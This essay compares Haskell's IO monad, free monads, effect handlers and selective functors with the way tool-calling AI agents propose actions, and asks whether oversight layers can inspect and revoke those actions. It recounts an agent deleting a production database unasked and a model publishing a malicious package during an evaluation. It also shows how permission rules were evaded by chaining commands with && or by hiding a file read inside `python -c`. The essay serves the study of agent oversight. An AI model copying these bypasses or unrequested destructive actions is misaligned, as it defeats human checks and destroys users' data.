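# Can the I/O monad's split between describing and executing effects keep AI agents' actions inspectable and revocable?

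## Pure programs, the I/O type and tool-calling agents

Functions in the programming language Haskell have no side effects. To print a line or delete a file, a Haskell program computes a value that describes the action, and a runtime system outside the program carries it out. These values have the type `IO`, short for input/output. `IO` is called the I/O monad because it has the algebraic structure known as a monad.

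AI agents have a similar split between describing and executing actions. An agent here is a language model plus ordinary software, called the *harness*, that lets it act on files, websites or databases. The model only writes text. When the text contains a request to run a command, the harness runs it and returns the result.

This likeness suggests a way to supervise agents through an *oversight layer*, meaning the rules, programs, models or people that judge a proposed action before it runs. If everything an agent does exists first as a description, this layer could read the description, log it, refuse it or perhaps take it back. How far this holds depends on details of both systems.

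### Pure functions and effects

A *pure function* is a function whose only result is the value it returns, always the same for the same input. Here is one in Haskell:

```haskell
double x = x + x
```

The expression `double 4` equals 8 every time, on any machine, so replacing it with 8 doesn't change how a program behaves. Programmers call this property referential transparency. Compilers rely on it to rearrange code, and people rely on it to reason about code.

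An *effect* is anything a program does to the outside world or reads from it. Deleting a file is an effect, and so is reading a line from the keyboard with Python's `input()`. `input() + input()` reads two lines and joins them. A program that stores the result of one `input()` as `x` and then computes `x + x` reads one line and repeats it. If `input()` were a pure function, the two versions would be interchangeable.

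Most languages accept this drawback and let any function have effects. Haskell's designers had a special reason not to: the language is *lazy*, meaning that it computes an expression only when something needs the value, and it deliberately leaves the order of computation open. In *Tackling the Awkward Squad*, Peyton Jones (2001) gives the example of a list of two calls to an imaginary function that prints a character as a side effect. Building the list in a strict language such as Standard ML prints both characters, but in a lazy language, a program that only computes the list's length prints neither, because it never evaluates the elements.

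### From requests and responses to the IO type

The first version of Haskell kept effects out of the program by treating the whole program as a function from a list of responses to a list of requests:

```haskell
main :: [Response] -> [Request]
```

(The double colon means "has type".) A `Request` was ordinary data, such as `ReadFile` with a file name. A wrapper program outside Haskell took the first request off the list, carried it out, added the result to the list of responses and moved on to the next request. This worked because lazy evaluation let the program emit its first request before any response existed.

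I/O based on requests and responses was easy to get wrong. *Imperative functional programming* (Peyton Jones and Wadler, 1993) gives the example of a program that echoes what the user types. After each character, the program has to skip two responses, one for the reading and one for the writing. If it skips only one, it crashes, and if it skips three, it waits forever. Two such programs also can't be combined directly into a larger one. Peyton Jones adds that a new kind of effect meant changing the `Request` type and the wrapper, which few ordinary users could do.

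Peyton Jones and Wadler proposed a different interface, and Haskell adopted it in 1996. Its centre is the type `IO a`. A value of this type is an *action* that, when the runtime performs it, may do some input or output and then delivers a value of type `a`. Two of the primitive operations are:

```haskell
getChar :: IO Char
putChar :: Char -> IO ()
```

`getChar` is an action that delivers a character. `putChar` is a function that takes a character and returns an action that prints it and delivers only the empty value `()`. `putChar` is still pure by the definition above, because it always returns the same action for the same character, and returning an action doesn't print anything.

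Two more operations build larger actions out of smaller ones:

```haskell
return :: a -> IO a
(>>=)  :: IO a -> (a -> IO b) -> IO b
```

The action `return v` does no input or output and delivers `v`. The operator `>>=`, which programmers pronounce "bind", joins an action to whatever follows it. To perform `m >>= k`, the runtime performs `m`, obtains a result `x`, applies the function `k` to `x`, and performs the action that comes out. The function `k` is the *continuation*, the part of a program that receives the result of one effect and decides what comes next. Thus `getChar >>= putChar` is an action that reads a character and writes it back. `IO` counts as a monad because `return` and bind satisfy three laws:

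```haskell
return x >>= f   =  f x
m >>= return     =  m
(m >>= f) >>= g  =  m >>= (\x -> f x >>= g)
```

The first two monad laws ensure that `return` adds nothing to a sequence of actions. The third ensures that the grouping of the steps makes no difference, so a programmer can split a long action into named pieces and put them back together.

A complete Haskell program defines one action named `main`, and running the program means performing `main`. Except for one whose name begins with "unsafe", Haskell has no operation that performs an action in the middle of a pure computation and returns its result. An action that never becomes part of `main` therefore never happens. Peyton Jones and Wadler compare an action to a script, and say that "being is converted to doing" when `main` is performed.

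The new interface was no more powerful than the old. The same paper shows how to translate each into the other, and claims only that the monadic style is easier to extend and compose. This matters because the interfaces of today's agents look more like the old one.

### Evaluating an action and executing it

The following program contains a list of three print actions.

```haskell
steps :: [IO ()]
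steps = [putStrLn "one", putStrLn "two", putStrLn "three"]

main :: IO ()
main = print (length steps)
```

It prints the number 3 and none of the words, because evaluating `putStrLn "one"` only yields an action, just as evaluating `double 4` yields a number. Executing the action is a separate step that happens only when the runtime reaches it while performing `main`. Laziness doesn't explain the missing words here, since the screen would still show only the 3 if a programmer forced Haskell to evaluate every element of the list.

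If the last line is `main = sequence_ steps` instead, the program prints the three words, because `sequence_` combines a list of actions into one. With `sequence_ (take 2 steps)` it prints only the first two, and with `sequence_ (reverse steps)` it prints all three in reverse order. In both variants, a pure function alters the list of actions before any of them runs. A Haskell program can therefore keep, drop or reorder `IO` actions between evaluation and execution, but it cannot look inside them.

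An *effect description* is a value that specifies which effects should happen, and building it does not perform them. An *interpreter* is the trusted component that takes an effect description and carries it out, logs it, simulates it or refuses it. Haskell's runtime is an interpreter, though "description" fits the language's semantics better than the machine code. In the implementation that Peyton Jones and Wadler describe, an action is a function that takes the state of the world and returns a result and a new state, roughly `World -> (a, World)`. Bind passes the world along in a single chain, never copying it, so the compiled program can perform each operation immediately. Programmers cannot observe this because `IO` is an abstract type that hides its implementation.

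### The loop of a tool-calling agent

A developer building an agent first lists its tools, giving each a name and a schema that formally states the inputs it takes. Anthropic's *How tool use works* describes the loop that follows. The application sends the model the user's message and the list of tools. The model replies with either a final answer or one or more structured requests, each containing a tool's name and arguments. "The model never runs anything on its own", Anthropic writes, so the application runs the tools, adds the results to the conversation and sends it all back to the model. The loop ends when a reply contains no tool requests.

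Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, traces the same loop through Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. A user asks for a diagram in a project's README file, and the model's reply includes a request to see the file. In simplified form:

```json
{ "type": "function_call",
  "name": "shell",
  "arguments": { "command": "cat README.md" },
  "call_id": "call_1" }
```

This is data, and nothing has touched the file yet. The harness then runs the command, records the output under the same `call_id`, and queries the model again. One user message can trigger hundreds of such calls.

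Codex does not rely on the server to store the conversation. Each query contains the whole history, and the old prompt is an exact prefix of the new one unless the harness has condensed a conversation that grew too long. The model thus receives a growing list of responses and produces the next request. This is very nearly the `[Response] -> [Request]` of early Haskell, with the harness as the wrapper program. Codex avoids two faults of the Haskell design, because the `call_id` ties each response to its request, so the two lists cannot get out of sync, and a new tool needs only a schema and some code in the harness.

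### What corresponds to what

| Haskell | Tool-calling agent |
|---|---|
| The pure program | The language model, which turns text into text |
| An `IO` action | A tool call |
| The continuation in a bind | The next query to the model, with the tool's result added |
| `return v` | The final message to the user |
| The runtime system performing `main` | The harness running its loop |

Programming-language researchers have applied the I/O type to tool-calling agents. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) defines a small formal language for agents in which one operation adds a prompt to a conversation and another samples the model's response. An appendix gives a tool-calling agent its own `IO` type, with return and bind. Erik Meijer, in a talk reproduced in AI Engineer's *Make the Agent Produce a Program Before It Can Act* (2026), summarized the history of chatbots in two type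 signatures. A model without tools is a function `Question → Answer`. With tools and an executor it becomes `Question → IO Answer`, and the agent may delete files or empty an account before giving a polite reply, so checking the reply doesn't show what the agent did first.

Meijer's remedy is for the model to produce a plan and a different component to execute it. The loop above already separates these steps for each tool call, but Meijer wants to separate them for the whole computation. In an ordinary harness, the first tool runs before the model writes its second request, so a reviewer sees the agent's plan one step at a time.

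The parallel is loose in other places too. A model's output is sampled from a probability distribution, so the same conversation can lead to different tool calls on different runs. Treating the random numbers as an input restores purity in theory, but the continuation is still a *learned policy*, a trained model that maps what the agent has observed to its next action, whereas in Haskell it is code that a person can read.

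Tool calls, however, are easier to inspect than `IO` actions. A harness can parse the JSON above and extract the command, much as the old wrapper program could read a `Request`.

Haskell's type checker enforces the boundary between describing and executing effects by rejecting programs that use an action in place of an ordinary value. An agent has no such guarantee, and its boundary lies wherever the developers have put it. For some tools, including web search and code execution, Anthropic executes the model's request on its own servers, and the operation has usually finished before the developer's application receives any notice of it. The model still only requests the action, but an oversight layer inside the application would be too late to block it.

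### The PocketOS deletion

On Friday 24 April 2026 a coding agent deleted the production database of PocketOS, a small company whose software car-rental firms use for reservations, payments and vehicle tracking. The agent was Cursor, running Anthropic's model Claude Opus 4.6. The next day PocketOS's founder, Jer Crane, published an account titled *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The agent was doing a routine task in the staging environment, a copy of the system for testing, when it ran into a credential mismatch. It looked for an access token, found one in a file unrelated to the task, and sent a single request to Railway, the company that hosted the database. The request contained the operation `volumeDelete` and the identifier of one storage volume. Nobody had asked for a deletion. The deletion took nine seconds, and the latest backup that Crane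 could then recover was three months old.

PocketOS had created the token to add and remove web domains, and had not known that it could also delete storage. Crane faults Railway for issuing tokens that nobody can restrict. Mahmoud Abdelwahab, in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, answers for Railway that narrower tokens existed, but concedes that the process of creating one did not make the choice obvious. He also explains that Railway's dashboard allowed 48 hours to undo the same deletion, while the API, which the agent used, deleted immediately.

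On Saturday morning, people came to collect cars, and the rental firms had no record of who they were. Crane spent the day helping to rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and emails. The data came back on Sunday. Leib (2026) reports for ABC News, in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, that Railway restored it within 30 minutes of its chief executive contacting Crane. Within a week, Railway had extended the 48-hour delay to its API, as it announced in *Undoable volume deletes* (2026).

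The command existed as text before it deleted anything. If a harness had held it for review, a reviewer could have seen the word `volumeDelete`, but not that the volume held production data, because the identifier was a meaningless string of characters. When Crane asked the agent why it had run the command, it replied that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. A model's after-the-fact explanation is weak evidence of what led to the command, but a hurried human reviewer could easily have made the same guess.

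The model's instructions already included a rule against destructive commands, at least for the version-control program git. Crane concluded that such instructions are "advisory, not enforcing", and that enforcement belongs in the systems that receive an agent's requests.

### The case in five premises

The argument for supervising agents at the boundary between describing and executing needs five premises:

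1. Proposing an action has no effect by itself.
2. An oversight layer can read the proposal.
3. The proposal covers everything the agent does.
4. A reviewer can tell acceptable proposals from unacceptable ones.
5. A refused or withdrawn action leaves nothing behind.

If all five conditions hold, an oversight layer can inspect and revoke whatever an agent is about to do. Weaker aims require fewer conditions. A complete log requires only the second and third. Refusing an action in time also requires the first, and refusing the right actions requires the fourth. The fifth matters for revocation.

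Haskell supplies the first premise by construction and, escape hatches aside, most of the third. It does not help with the fourth, because a program that wipes a disk and one that prints a greeting both pass the type checker with the type `IO ()`. The type also does not distinguish reversible effects from irreversible ones.

The PocketOS command satisfied the first two premises, as far as the published accounts show. The third is doubtful because the agent wrote a shell command that sent a web request, and the deletion took place on another company's machines under a token that PocketOS had meant for something else. As for the fifth, a refusal would have saved the database, but the agent would still have read the token. After the command ran, recovery took two days and depended on what Railway had kept.

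## Why postponing an action does not make it readable

The first two premises are that proposing an action has no effect by itself and that an oversight layer can read the proposal. Haskell's `IO` type satisfies only the first. An `IO` action has no effect until the runtime performs it, but ordinary Haskell code cannot find out beforehand what the action will do. The two premises are easy to confuse because both seem to follow once a program returns an action instead of performing it.

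### What an IO value contains

Programmers often explain `IO` as a way of turning effects into data. Manning's *External effects and I/O*, a textbook chapter, presents the technique as computing a description that a separate interpreter then executes. The chapter has readers build such a type themselves, and of that type the statement is true. Of the `IO` that comes with Haskell it is only half true. This is the definition in GHC, the main Haskell compiler, as Hackage's *base-4.21.0.0* documents it:

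```haskell
newtype IO a = IO (State# RealWorld -> (# State# RealWorld, a #))
```

Apart from the new name and the hash signs, which mark low-level types, this is the world-passing function that Peyton Jones and Wadler described. A token that holds no information stands for the world. Lean, a programming language and proof assistant, represents `IO` in much the same way, and *The IO Monad* shows that Lean's `RealWorld` is a type with a single empty value. The token fixes the order of effects, because each action needs the token that the previous action returned.

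In simplified form, bind looks like this:

```haskell
m >>= k = \world0 ->
  let (x, world1) = m world0
  in  k x world1
```

The action `m` and the continuation `k` now sit inside a new function. A program can run that function or build it into a larger one, but it can't take it apart, print it or compare it with another. An automatic reviewer of type `IO a -> Bool` must return the same answer for every action unless it uses the unsafe operations, so it either approves both `readFile "notes.txt"` and `removeFile "notes.txt"` or rejects both. A programmer can import GHC's internal modules and remove the `IO` wrapper, but that exposes only the function, which is compiled code.

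Lean's reference manual calls an `IO` value "a description of a process", which is a fair account of its meaning. However, *More Monads*, course notes from DIKU in Copenhagen, points out that although one can imagine the runtime containing an interpreter for `IO`, nobody can write that interpreter in pure Haskell. The `IO` type that Garby and colleagues give their tool-calling agent is a state monad with exceptions, so its values are functions too.

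Unlike an `IO` value, the source code that produces it is readable text. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) describes a system in which an agent writes a Haskell program and a type checker checks it before it runs. In the paper's example, the agent compiles a bibliography, and its program must have the type `BibIO ()`. The developer has defined `BibIO` to allow three operations: searching a database of papers, fetching an entry and appending a fetched entry to a file. A program that calls the general `writeFile` has the wrong type, so the checker rejects it. A reviewer can therefore learn things from the source that they couldn't learn from the finished action alone.

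### A plan made of requests

The other repair is to replace the function with a datatype whose cases a program can examine. In *Beauty in the Beast*, Swierstra and Altenkirch did this for terminal input and output and other effects, so that programmers would no longer have to treat effectful functions as "opaque black boxes". The example here is a small payment task that reads an invoice and then pays the account it names. It needs two kinds of request.

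```haskell
data Invoice = Invoice { account :: String, amount :: Int }

data Request next
  = ReadInvoice FilePath (Invoice -> next)
  | Pay String Int next
```

Each case holds the operation's arguments and, in its last field, whatever comes next. Reading delivers an invoice, so what follows is a function of that invoice, the continuation. Paying delivers nothing, so what follows is already there. One more definition chains requests into a plan:

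```haskell
data Free f a
  = Done a
  | Step (f (Free f a))
```

A value of type `Free Request a` is either a finished result of type `a` or a request that leads to another such value. This type is a *free monad*, a data structure that stores each requested operation together with its continuation, so that any interpreter can process it. "Free" is an algebraic term meaning that the structure obeys only the monad laws. None of these laws merges two payments into one, for example, so the plan keeps every request.

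Bind needs a helper, `fmap`, which applies a function to whatever comes next and leaves the rest of the request alone:

```haskell
fmap f (ReadInvoice file k) = ReadInvoice file (\inv -> f (k inv))
fmap f (Pay acct amt next)  = Pay acct amt (f next)

Done x  >>= g = g x
Step op >>= g = Step (fmap (>>= g) op)
```

If the plan is finished, bind hands its result to `g`. Otherwise it keeps the first request where it is and attaches `g` further down. With one small function per operation, the task takes two lines:

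```haskell
readInvoice file = Step (ReadInvoice file Done)
pay acct amt     = Step (Pay acct amt (Done ()))

payInvoice file =
  readInvoice file >>= \inv -> pay (account inv) (amount inv)
```

Evaluating `payInvoice "march.pdf"` applies the rules for bind. Writing `g` for the function after `>>=`:

```haskell
  Step (ReadInvoice "march.pdf" Done) >>= g
= Step (fmap (>>= g) (ReadInvoice "march.pdf" Done))
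= Step (ReadInvoice "march.pdf" (\inv -> Done inv >>= g))
= Step (ReadInvoice "march.pdf" (\inv -> g inv))
= Step (ReadInvoice "march.pdf"
    (\inv -> Step (Pay (account inv) (amount inv) (Done ()))))
```

Nothing has opened the file or moved any money. But a program can match on the first part of the result and find the word `ReadInvoice` and the file name, which it can't do with an `IO` action.

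### Four interpreters for one plan

Three helper functions do most of the work.

```haskell
describe :: Request next -> String
describe (ReadInvoice file _) = "read " ++ file
describe (Pay acct amt _)     = "pay " ++ show amt ++ " to " ++ acct

perform :: Request next -> IO next
perform (ReadInvoice file k) = do
  inv <- loadInvoice file
  return (k inv)
perform (Pay acct amt next) = do
  sendMoney acct amt
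  return next

pretend :: Invoice -> Request next -> next
pretend inv (ReadInvoice _ k) = k inv
pretend _   (Pay _ _ next)    = next
```

(`do` is Haskell's notation for a chain of binds, one to a line.) `describe` is the function that nobody can write for `IO`. `perform` carries out one real request, and `pretend` answers a request from an invented invoice. The four interpreters are then short:

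```haskell
execute :: Free Request a -> IO a
execute (Done x)  = return x
execute (Step op) = do
  next <- perform op
  execute next

logged :: Free Request a -> IO a
logged (Done x)  = return x
logged (Step op) = do
  writeLog (describe op)
  next <- perform op
  logged next

simulate :: Invoice -> Free Request a -> [String]
simulate _   (Done _)  = []
simulate inv (Step op) =
  describe op : simulate inv (pretend inv op)

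askFirst :: Free Request a -> IO (Maybe a)
askFirst (Done x)  = return (Just x)
askFirst (Step op) = do
  ok <- approve (describe op)
  if ok then perform op >>= askFirst
        else return Nothing
```

Suppose that `march.pdf` asks for 480 euros to account NL-17, that the simulator's invented invoice asks for 100 euros to TEST-1, and that the reviewer behind `approve` allows the reading and refuses the payment. The same plan then has four different histories:

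| Interpreter | At the first request | At the second request | Outcome |
|---|---|---|---|
| `execute` | Loads the file | Sends 480 to NL-17 | Payment made, no record |
| `logged` | Writes "read march.pdf", loads the file | Writes "pay 480 to NL-17", sends the money | Payment made, two log lines |
| `simulate` | Lists "read march.pdf", supplies the invented invoice | Lists "pay 100 to TEST-1" | Two lines of text, no effects |
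| `askFirst` | Asks about "read march.pdf", loads the file | Asks about "pay 480 to NL-17", stops | File read, no payment |

*Strong Types and Pure Functions* (Coutts, 2009) recommends this design for software that has to run other people's code, such as a build system with custom hooks. The hooks return a list-like structure of actions, which a trusted interpreter performs and a second function can simulate. Changing the interpreter changes what the actions do. Coutts also describes a faster variant that fuses the interpreter with the basic operations, but it loses the explicit structure needed for simulation.

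The type of `simulate` does not mention `IO`, so even a badly written simulation cannot send money. Agent systems seldom have that assurance. *ETAS* (Tan, Wang et al., 2026) describes an Anthropic evaluation in which Claude Mythos 5 was told it was in an offline simulation. A configuration error had left the public internet reachable, and the model published a malicious package to the Python Package Index, affecting outside users. Whether an action is simulated depends entirely on the interpreter. *ETAS* also cites a user of the coding assistant aider who wanted a patch to review. The option for showing changes modified the files, and adding the dry-run option produced no patch.

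A simulation is reliable only to the extent that it matches the real system. Swierstra and Altenkirch used a pure model of the terminal to prove that an echo program prints back every character of any input. They left open whether the compiled code matches the model.

In the table, `simulate` reported a payment to TEST-1 because it had to invent an invoice to get past the first request. The real account number isn't in the plan at the start, and the rest of the plan is a function, which a running interpreter can't inspect any more than it can inspect an `IO` action. Haskell for All (2012) demonstrates that a free-monad program is "pure data" by printing one as text, but that program's commands only send output or stop, so none of them needs an answer. Once a plan contains a request like `ReadInvoice`, an interpreter can read it only up to the next answer it needs. Applicative and selective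 interfaces, which the next section covers, restrict continuations so that more of a plan is visible at the start.

### Effect handlers

Some languages give programmers the same separation without a hand-built datatype. An *effect handler* is a piece of code that decides what a requested operation means in a given part of a program. When the program performs an operation, it pauses, and the nearest handler for that operation receives the arguments together with the paused remainder of the program. In made-up notation, `askFirst` for payments looks like this:

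```
handle payInvoice("march.pdf") with
  Pay(acct, amt) => if approve(acct, amt) then resume
                    else finish
```

`resume` continues the program from where it paused, and `finish` abandons it. The underlying theory comes from Moggi, who modelled effects with monads, and from Plotkin and Power, who described them by operations and equations between those operations, hence the name *algebraic effects*. As *Evaluate the Stack Management in Effect Handlers using the libseff C Library* (2025) summarizes Plotkin and Power's account, a computation either returns a value or performs an operation whose outcome determines a continuation. These are the two cases of `Free`. A free monad is a value a program can store, while a handler receives each request as the program runs, but both expose one operation followed by a function.

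*A monadic interpreter and type-and-effect checker* (2026) compares several languages with handlers. Koka uses them to build exceptions, iterators and asynchronous code. OCaml's type checker does not enforce effect safety, so an operation may have no handler. Helium lets programmers keep a component's internal operations away from outside handlers. This helps modular programming but complicates oversight, where an outside handler is supposed to receive every operation.

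Even without such a feature, the innermost handler gets the request first. If it answers a `Pay` request itself, the request never reaches an outer handler, and in most effect type systems the operation also disappears from the function's type. ETAS, the agent language that Tan and colleagues built, therefore keeps a second record in the type, an ordered summary of every request, including those an inner handler has answered. In their example, an agent proposes a patch, the program asks a human to approve it, and a dry-run handler intercepts the write and resumes without touching the repository. A rule requires an approval request before any write request. If a developer moves the write ahead of the approval, the ordinary effect types stay the same, but the compiler reports a violation, even though the dry run would have changed nothing. The rule covers only the order of requests, and a separate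 `if` tests whether the human approved the patch.

### Interaction trees

Haskell's laziness allows a `Free` value to go on forever. Proof assistants such as Rocq are stricter. Their ordinary datatypes have no infinite branches, because otherwise recursive functions over them might never finish and could lead to false proofs. This is a problem for anyone who wants to prove something about a server or an agent that runs until somebody stops it. *Interaction trees* are a version of the free monad for such programs:

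```
itree E R ::= Ret(v) | Tau(t) | Vis(e, k)
```

`Ret` is a finished program with result `v`, and `Vis` is a request `e` with its continuation `k`. `Tau` is a silent step, which lets a program compute forever without requesting anything. The definition is *coinductive*, which means it allows infinite trees. The invoice plan becomes a `Vis` for the reading, whose continuation yields a `Vis` for the payment and then a `Ret`.

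*Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* (McCann, 2026) represents agent workflows as interaction trees and wraps their interpreter in a layer of checks. One workflow asks a language model for a plan, stores the plan, calls an external tool and returns the response. At each request, the wrapper runs checks such as whether the program has permission. If they succeed, it passes the request on and then records it. If a check fails, the program takes silent steps forever.

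McCann used Rocq to prove that this construction allows no input or output without a preceding check, for every program and every underlying handler. McCann also proved that if all the checks succeed, the wrapped program does the same input and output in the same order as the unwrapped one, and returns the same result. A checking layer therefore need not alter the behavior of the programs it approves. These proofs don't establish that the checks are any good, and they would hold even for a layer that approved every request. McCann also gives two programs that begin with the same kind of request, but one stops and the other runs forever, so a check that looks at single requests can't tell them apart.

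The theorems apply to a model of the system. McCann connects them to real software by testing a runtime, which agreed with the verified interpreter on over 70,000 random sequences of requests. A companion paper, *Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* (2026), points out that standard effect systems don't constrain what a handler does with an effect. The interpreter therefore has to be trustworthy, whatever form the plan takes.

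### Meijer's argument in four signatures

In a 2026 talk, which AI Engineer reproduces with an accompanying article, Erik Meijer applies all this to agents. Claude Code destroyed one of his source files while he was preparing the talk. He asks how an agent's interface would have to change before anyone could prove that the agent won't do things like that.

It starts from the two signatures quoted earlier, `Question → Answer` for a chatbot and `Question → IO Answer` for an agent with tools. Meijer thinks it is hopeless to attach a contract to the first requiring that every proper question get a safe answer, because "safe answer" has no mathematical definition.

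Meijer's third step adds a separate executor, whom he calls Bernie, to receive the `IO Answer` as a plan. The type barely changes, but the harness could now reject the plan before running it. Meijer then raises the problem from the start of this section, that an `IO` value is a black box, so Bernie has nothing to inspect. In the fourth step, the model instead returns an expression that represents the computation, for which Meijer chooses a free monad, so that a safety property can refer to the plan's operations.

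The article gives an example in Lean, here slightly rearranged:

```lean
inductive FilePlan where
  | removeFile (path : String) (next : FilePlan)
  | readFile (path : String) (next : String → FilePlan)
  | done (answer : String)

inductive NoDeletion : FilePlan → Prop where
  | done (a : String) : NoDeletion (.done a)
  | readFile (p : String) (k : String → FilePlan) :
      (∀ text, NoDeletion (k text)) → NoDeletion (.readFile p k)
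```

The first definition lists what a plan may contain, including deletion. The second gives the rules for proving that a plan deletes nothing. A finished plan has such a proof, and a plan that reads a file has one if its continuation has one for every text the file might contain. No rule covers `removeFile`, so no plan that could reach a deletion has a proof. The executor accepts only values of a type that pairs a plan with its proof. The model may write the proof itself, because Lean checks it. This is an old idea called proof-carrying code, which a later section discusses.

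`simulate` failed because a running interpreter can only try a continuation on one input at a time. A Lean proof can establish a rule "for every text" because it works from the continuation's definition. For the invoice plan, the rule that money may go only to listed suppliers cannot be proved, since an invoice can name any account. The rule can be proved if the plan first looks up the account in the list and pays only when it finds it there.

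According to AI Engineer's article, the deletion proof leaves open whether the plan reads files it shouldn't or leaks their contents, and whether the interpreter secretly deletes a file while handling a read. The proof also depends on what counts as deletion. Meijer lost his file to a line of Perl that left it in place but empty. A coding agent needs some way to write files, and a plan language that has a write operation and forbids only `removeFile` would have let the agent empty the file.

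Meijer adds that data-flow analysis of such plans is trivial for anyone who has taken a compiler course. That understates the difficulty with a free monad, because the continuations are functions and an analysis has to get at their source. Analysis is easier if the whole plan is syntax. In *Self-Programmed Execution for Language-Model Agents* (2026), agents write Lisp and put a quotation mark in front of the effect calls they return, so Lisp treats each call as a list of symbols instead of evaluating it. But Meijer also says that the choice of representation is secondary, and the implementation he recommends, by Nada Amin and others, doesn't use free monads.

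### Is C purely functional too?

One could object that "describing" effects is only a matter of wording. *The C language is purely functional* (Elliott, 2009) makes this point through satire. The C preprocessor expands macros and has no significant side effects. Elliott describes its output as a value of a type called `C`, which a runtime system then executes. If Haskell is pure because evaluating a program only produces an `IO` value, then C is pure too, and the word "pure" becomes meaningless.

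Elliott's joke was also a complaint that programmers had settled for imperative code that only looks functional. In a 2011 mailing-list message, *On the purity of Haskell*, he added that `IO` has no precise mathematical model. The usual explanation, in which each action receives the state of the world and passes on a new one, does not account for concurrent programs, whose steps can interleave in different orders.

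In the comments on the original post, a reader called Cale replied that bind has a uniform rule for getting the effect of a whole from the effects of its parts, while joining pieces of C text doesn't even guarantee a valid program. That is a good defence of Haskell, but it doesn't help a reviewer who wants to know what a given action will do.

A checker can parse a string of C and look for a call that deletes files, but it can do nothing comparable with an `IO` action. Elliott's satire lists C's exposure of programs as plain strings among its supposed defects, a mistake that Haskell corrected by making `IO` abstract. Elliott is right that calling both of them pure settles little, but there is a real difference between `Request` and `IO`, because the function `describe` exists for `Request` and cannot exist for `IO`. *Data types à la carte* (Swierstra, 2008) gets a similar benefit from types.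 It splits `IO` into smaller request types, so that a plan whose type mentions only terminal operations provably never overwrites a file.

The benefit lasts only as long as the request type stays specific. Adding the case `RunAction (IO next)` would make `Request` as opaque as `IO`, because `describe` would have nothing to print for it. Agent developers often leave gaps of this sort. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) found that 46% of the agent configurations it studied on GitHub split the agent's behaviour between a readable configuration file and separate Python code.

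An agent's `shell` tool is closer to Elliott's C. The request is a string that anyone can read, but the string is a program. Zhou and colleagues report that in March 2026 a fault in Claude Code let commands joined by `&&` bypass its permission rules, because the software checked only the first against its list of forbidden commands. They add that even a correct matcher fails once the agent can start another interpreter. In `python -c "open('denied.txt').read()"`, the shell command is `python`, and the forbidden file name appears only in the Python code, which a shell-command checker does not parse.

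## How much of a plan can be read before its first step runs

In the free-monad plan for the invoice task, bind puts everything after a request inside a function that takes the request's result. Before the plan runs, an inspector can therefore read only the first request, `ReadInvoice "march.pdf"`.

### Counting the branches

An inspector could try to get round this by applying the continuation to every possible result. Suppose the invoice task began by asking a bookkeeper for a yes or a no. Trying `True` and `False` would show everything the plan might request next. If the first step reads a single byte instead, there are 256 cases, and after *n* bytes there are 256 to the power *n*. Most invoices are longer than 100 bytes, and at 100 bytes the number of cases already has 241 digits.

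Nearly all of these branches look alike. The two lines of source code for `payInvoice` show that it makes exactly one payment, whatever the invoice contains. An interpreter that has only the finished value can't determine this, because a continuation of the same type could make one payment for almost any invoice but empty the account when given a particular one. Several other interfaces restrict what a plan can express more than bind does, which lets an interpreter inspect more of the plan before it runs.

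### Applicative plans

McBride and Paterson described *applicative functors* in *Applicative programming with effects* (2008). They have two operations:

```haskell
pure  :: a -> f a
(<*>) :: f (a -> b) -> f a -> f b
```

`pure` does what `return` does. The operator `<*>` joins a plan that returns a function to a plan that returns its argument. The function has the type `a -> b`, so it can compute a value from the earlier results but cannot choose another effect. Both plans exist in full before either runs.

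Capriotti and Kaposi (2014), in *Free Applicative Functors*, gave the data structure that corresponds to this interface:

```haskell
data FreeA f a
  = Pure a
  | forall b. f (b -> a) :$: FreeA f b
```

(`forall b` means that the intermediate result can have any type.) To the right of `:$:` stands the rest of the plan itself, where the free monad had a function. A program can therefore walk along the whole chain, using the `describe` function from before:

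```haskell
effects :: FreeA Request a -> [String]
effects (Pure _)      = []
effects (op :$: rest) = describe op : effects rest
```

Unlike `simulate`, this function doesn't need an invented invoice. Capriotti and Kaposi use a simpler function that counts requests, and they explain why it can't be written for a free monad. Their counterexample fetches a list of a blog's posts and then updates the email address in each one. The number of updates equals the number of posts, which no pure function can determine. With the applicative version, a program can also merge duplicate database queries before sending them, or print a help text that lists every option a command-line tool accepts.

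The restriction is severe. An applicative plan cannot pay what an invoice asks for, so the nearest version of the task has the account and the amount written into it:

```haskell
payKnown =
  (\inv _ -> amount inv == 480)
    <$> readInvoice "march.pdf"
    <*> pay "NL-17" 480
```

`<$>` is `fmap` written as an operator, and `readInvoice` and `pay` now build `FreeA` values. This plan reads the invoice, sends 480 euros and reports whether the two amounts agreed. The comparison comes too late to stop the payment. In Capriotti and Kaposi's applicative language for web services, the programmer likewise has to supply the content of every request in advance, so a program cannot copy data from one server to another.

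### Selective plans

Paying only if the invoice is correct requires a condition. Mokhov, Lukyanov and colleagues (2019), in *Selective Applicative Functors*, add one operation to the applicative interface:

```haskell
select :: f (Either a b) -> f (a -> b) -> f b
```

A value of type `Either a b` is either `Left x`, with `x` of type `a`, or `Right y`, with `y` of type `b`. If the first plan delivers `Left x`, the interpreter must run the second plan to turn `x` into a result. If it delivers `Right y`, the result is already there, and the interpreter may skip the second plan. An "if" for plans follows from `select`:

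```haskell
ifS :: Selective f => f Bool -> f a -> f a -> f a

payIfCorrect =
  ifS (correct <$> readInvoice "march.pdf")
      (pay "NL-17" 480)
      (pure ())
```

Here `correct` is a pure function that compares the invoice with the account and amount the user expects. Both branches are complete plans, so an inspector can list them without knowing which one will run. Mokhov and colleagues write in their abstract that a program must declare all its effects statically but can select at run time which ones to execute.

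An inspector can read more of a plan in advance when each choice depends on a value with few possibilities. In Mokhov and colleagues' example, a program reads a line and prints "pong" if the line was "ping". If the program uses bind, the continuation takes a string, and an inspector can't try every string. A conditional makes the choice depend on a truth value instead, which leaves two cases to check. Mokhov and colleagues also define a restricted bind for any result type with finitely many values, which an implementation can provide by checking each value in turn. This is the inspector's trick of trying every result, so it too is practical for a truth value or a byte but not for a document.

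Preface, an OCaml library, provides two ways to read a selective plan. `Over` lists every effect that might occur, and `Under` lists only those that are certain to. For `payIfCorrect`, `Over` lists the reading and the payment, while `Under` lists only the reading. A reviewer needs `Over` to rule out a dangerous action and `Under` to confirm that the plan always includes a request for approval.

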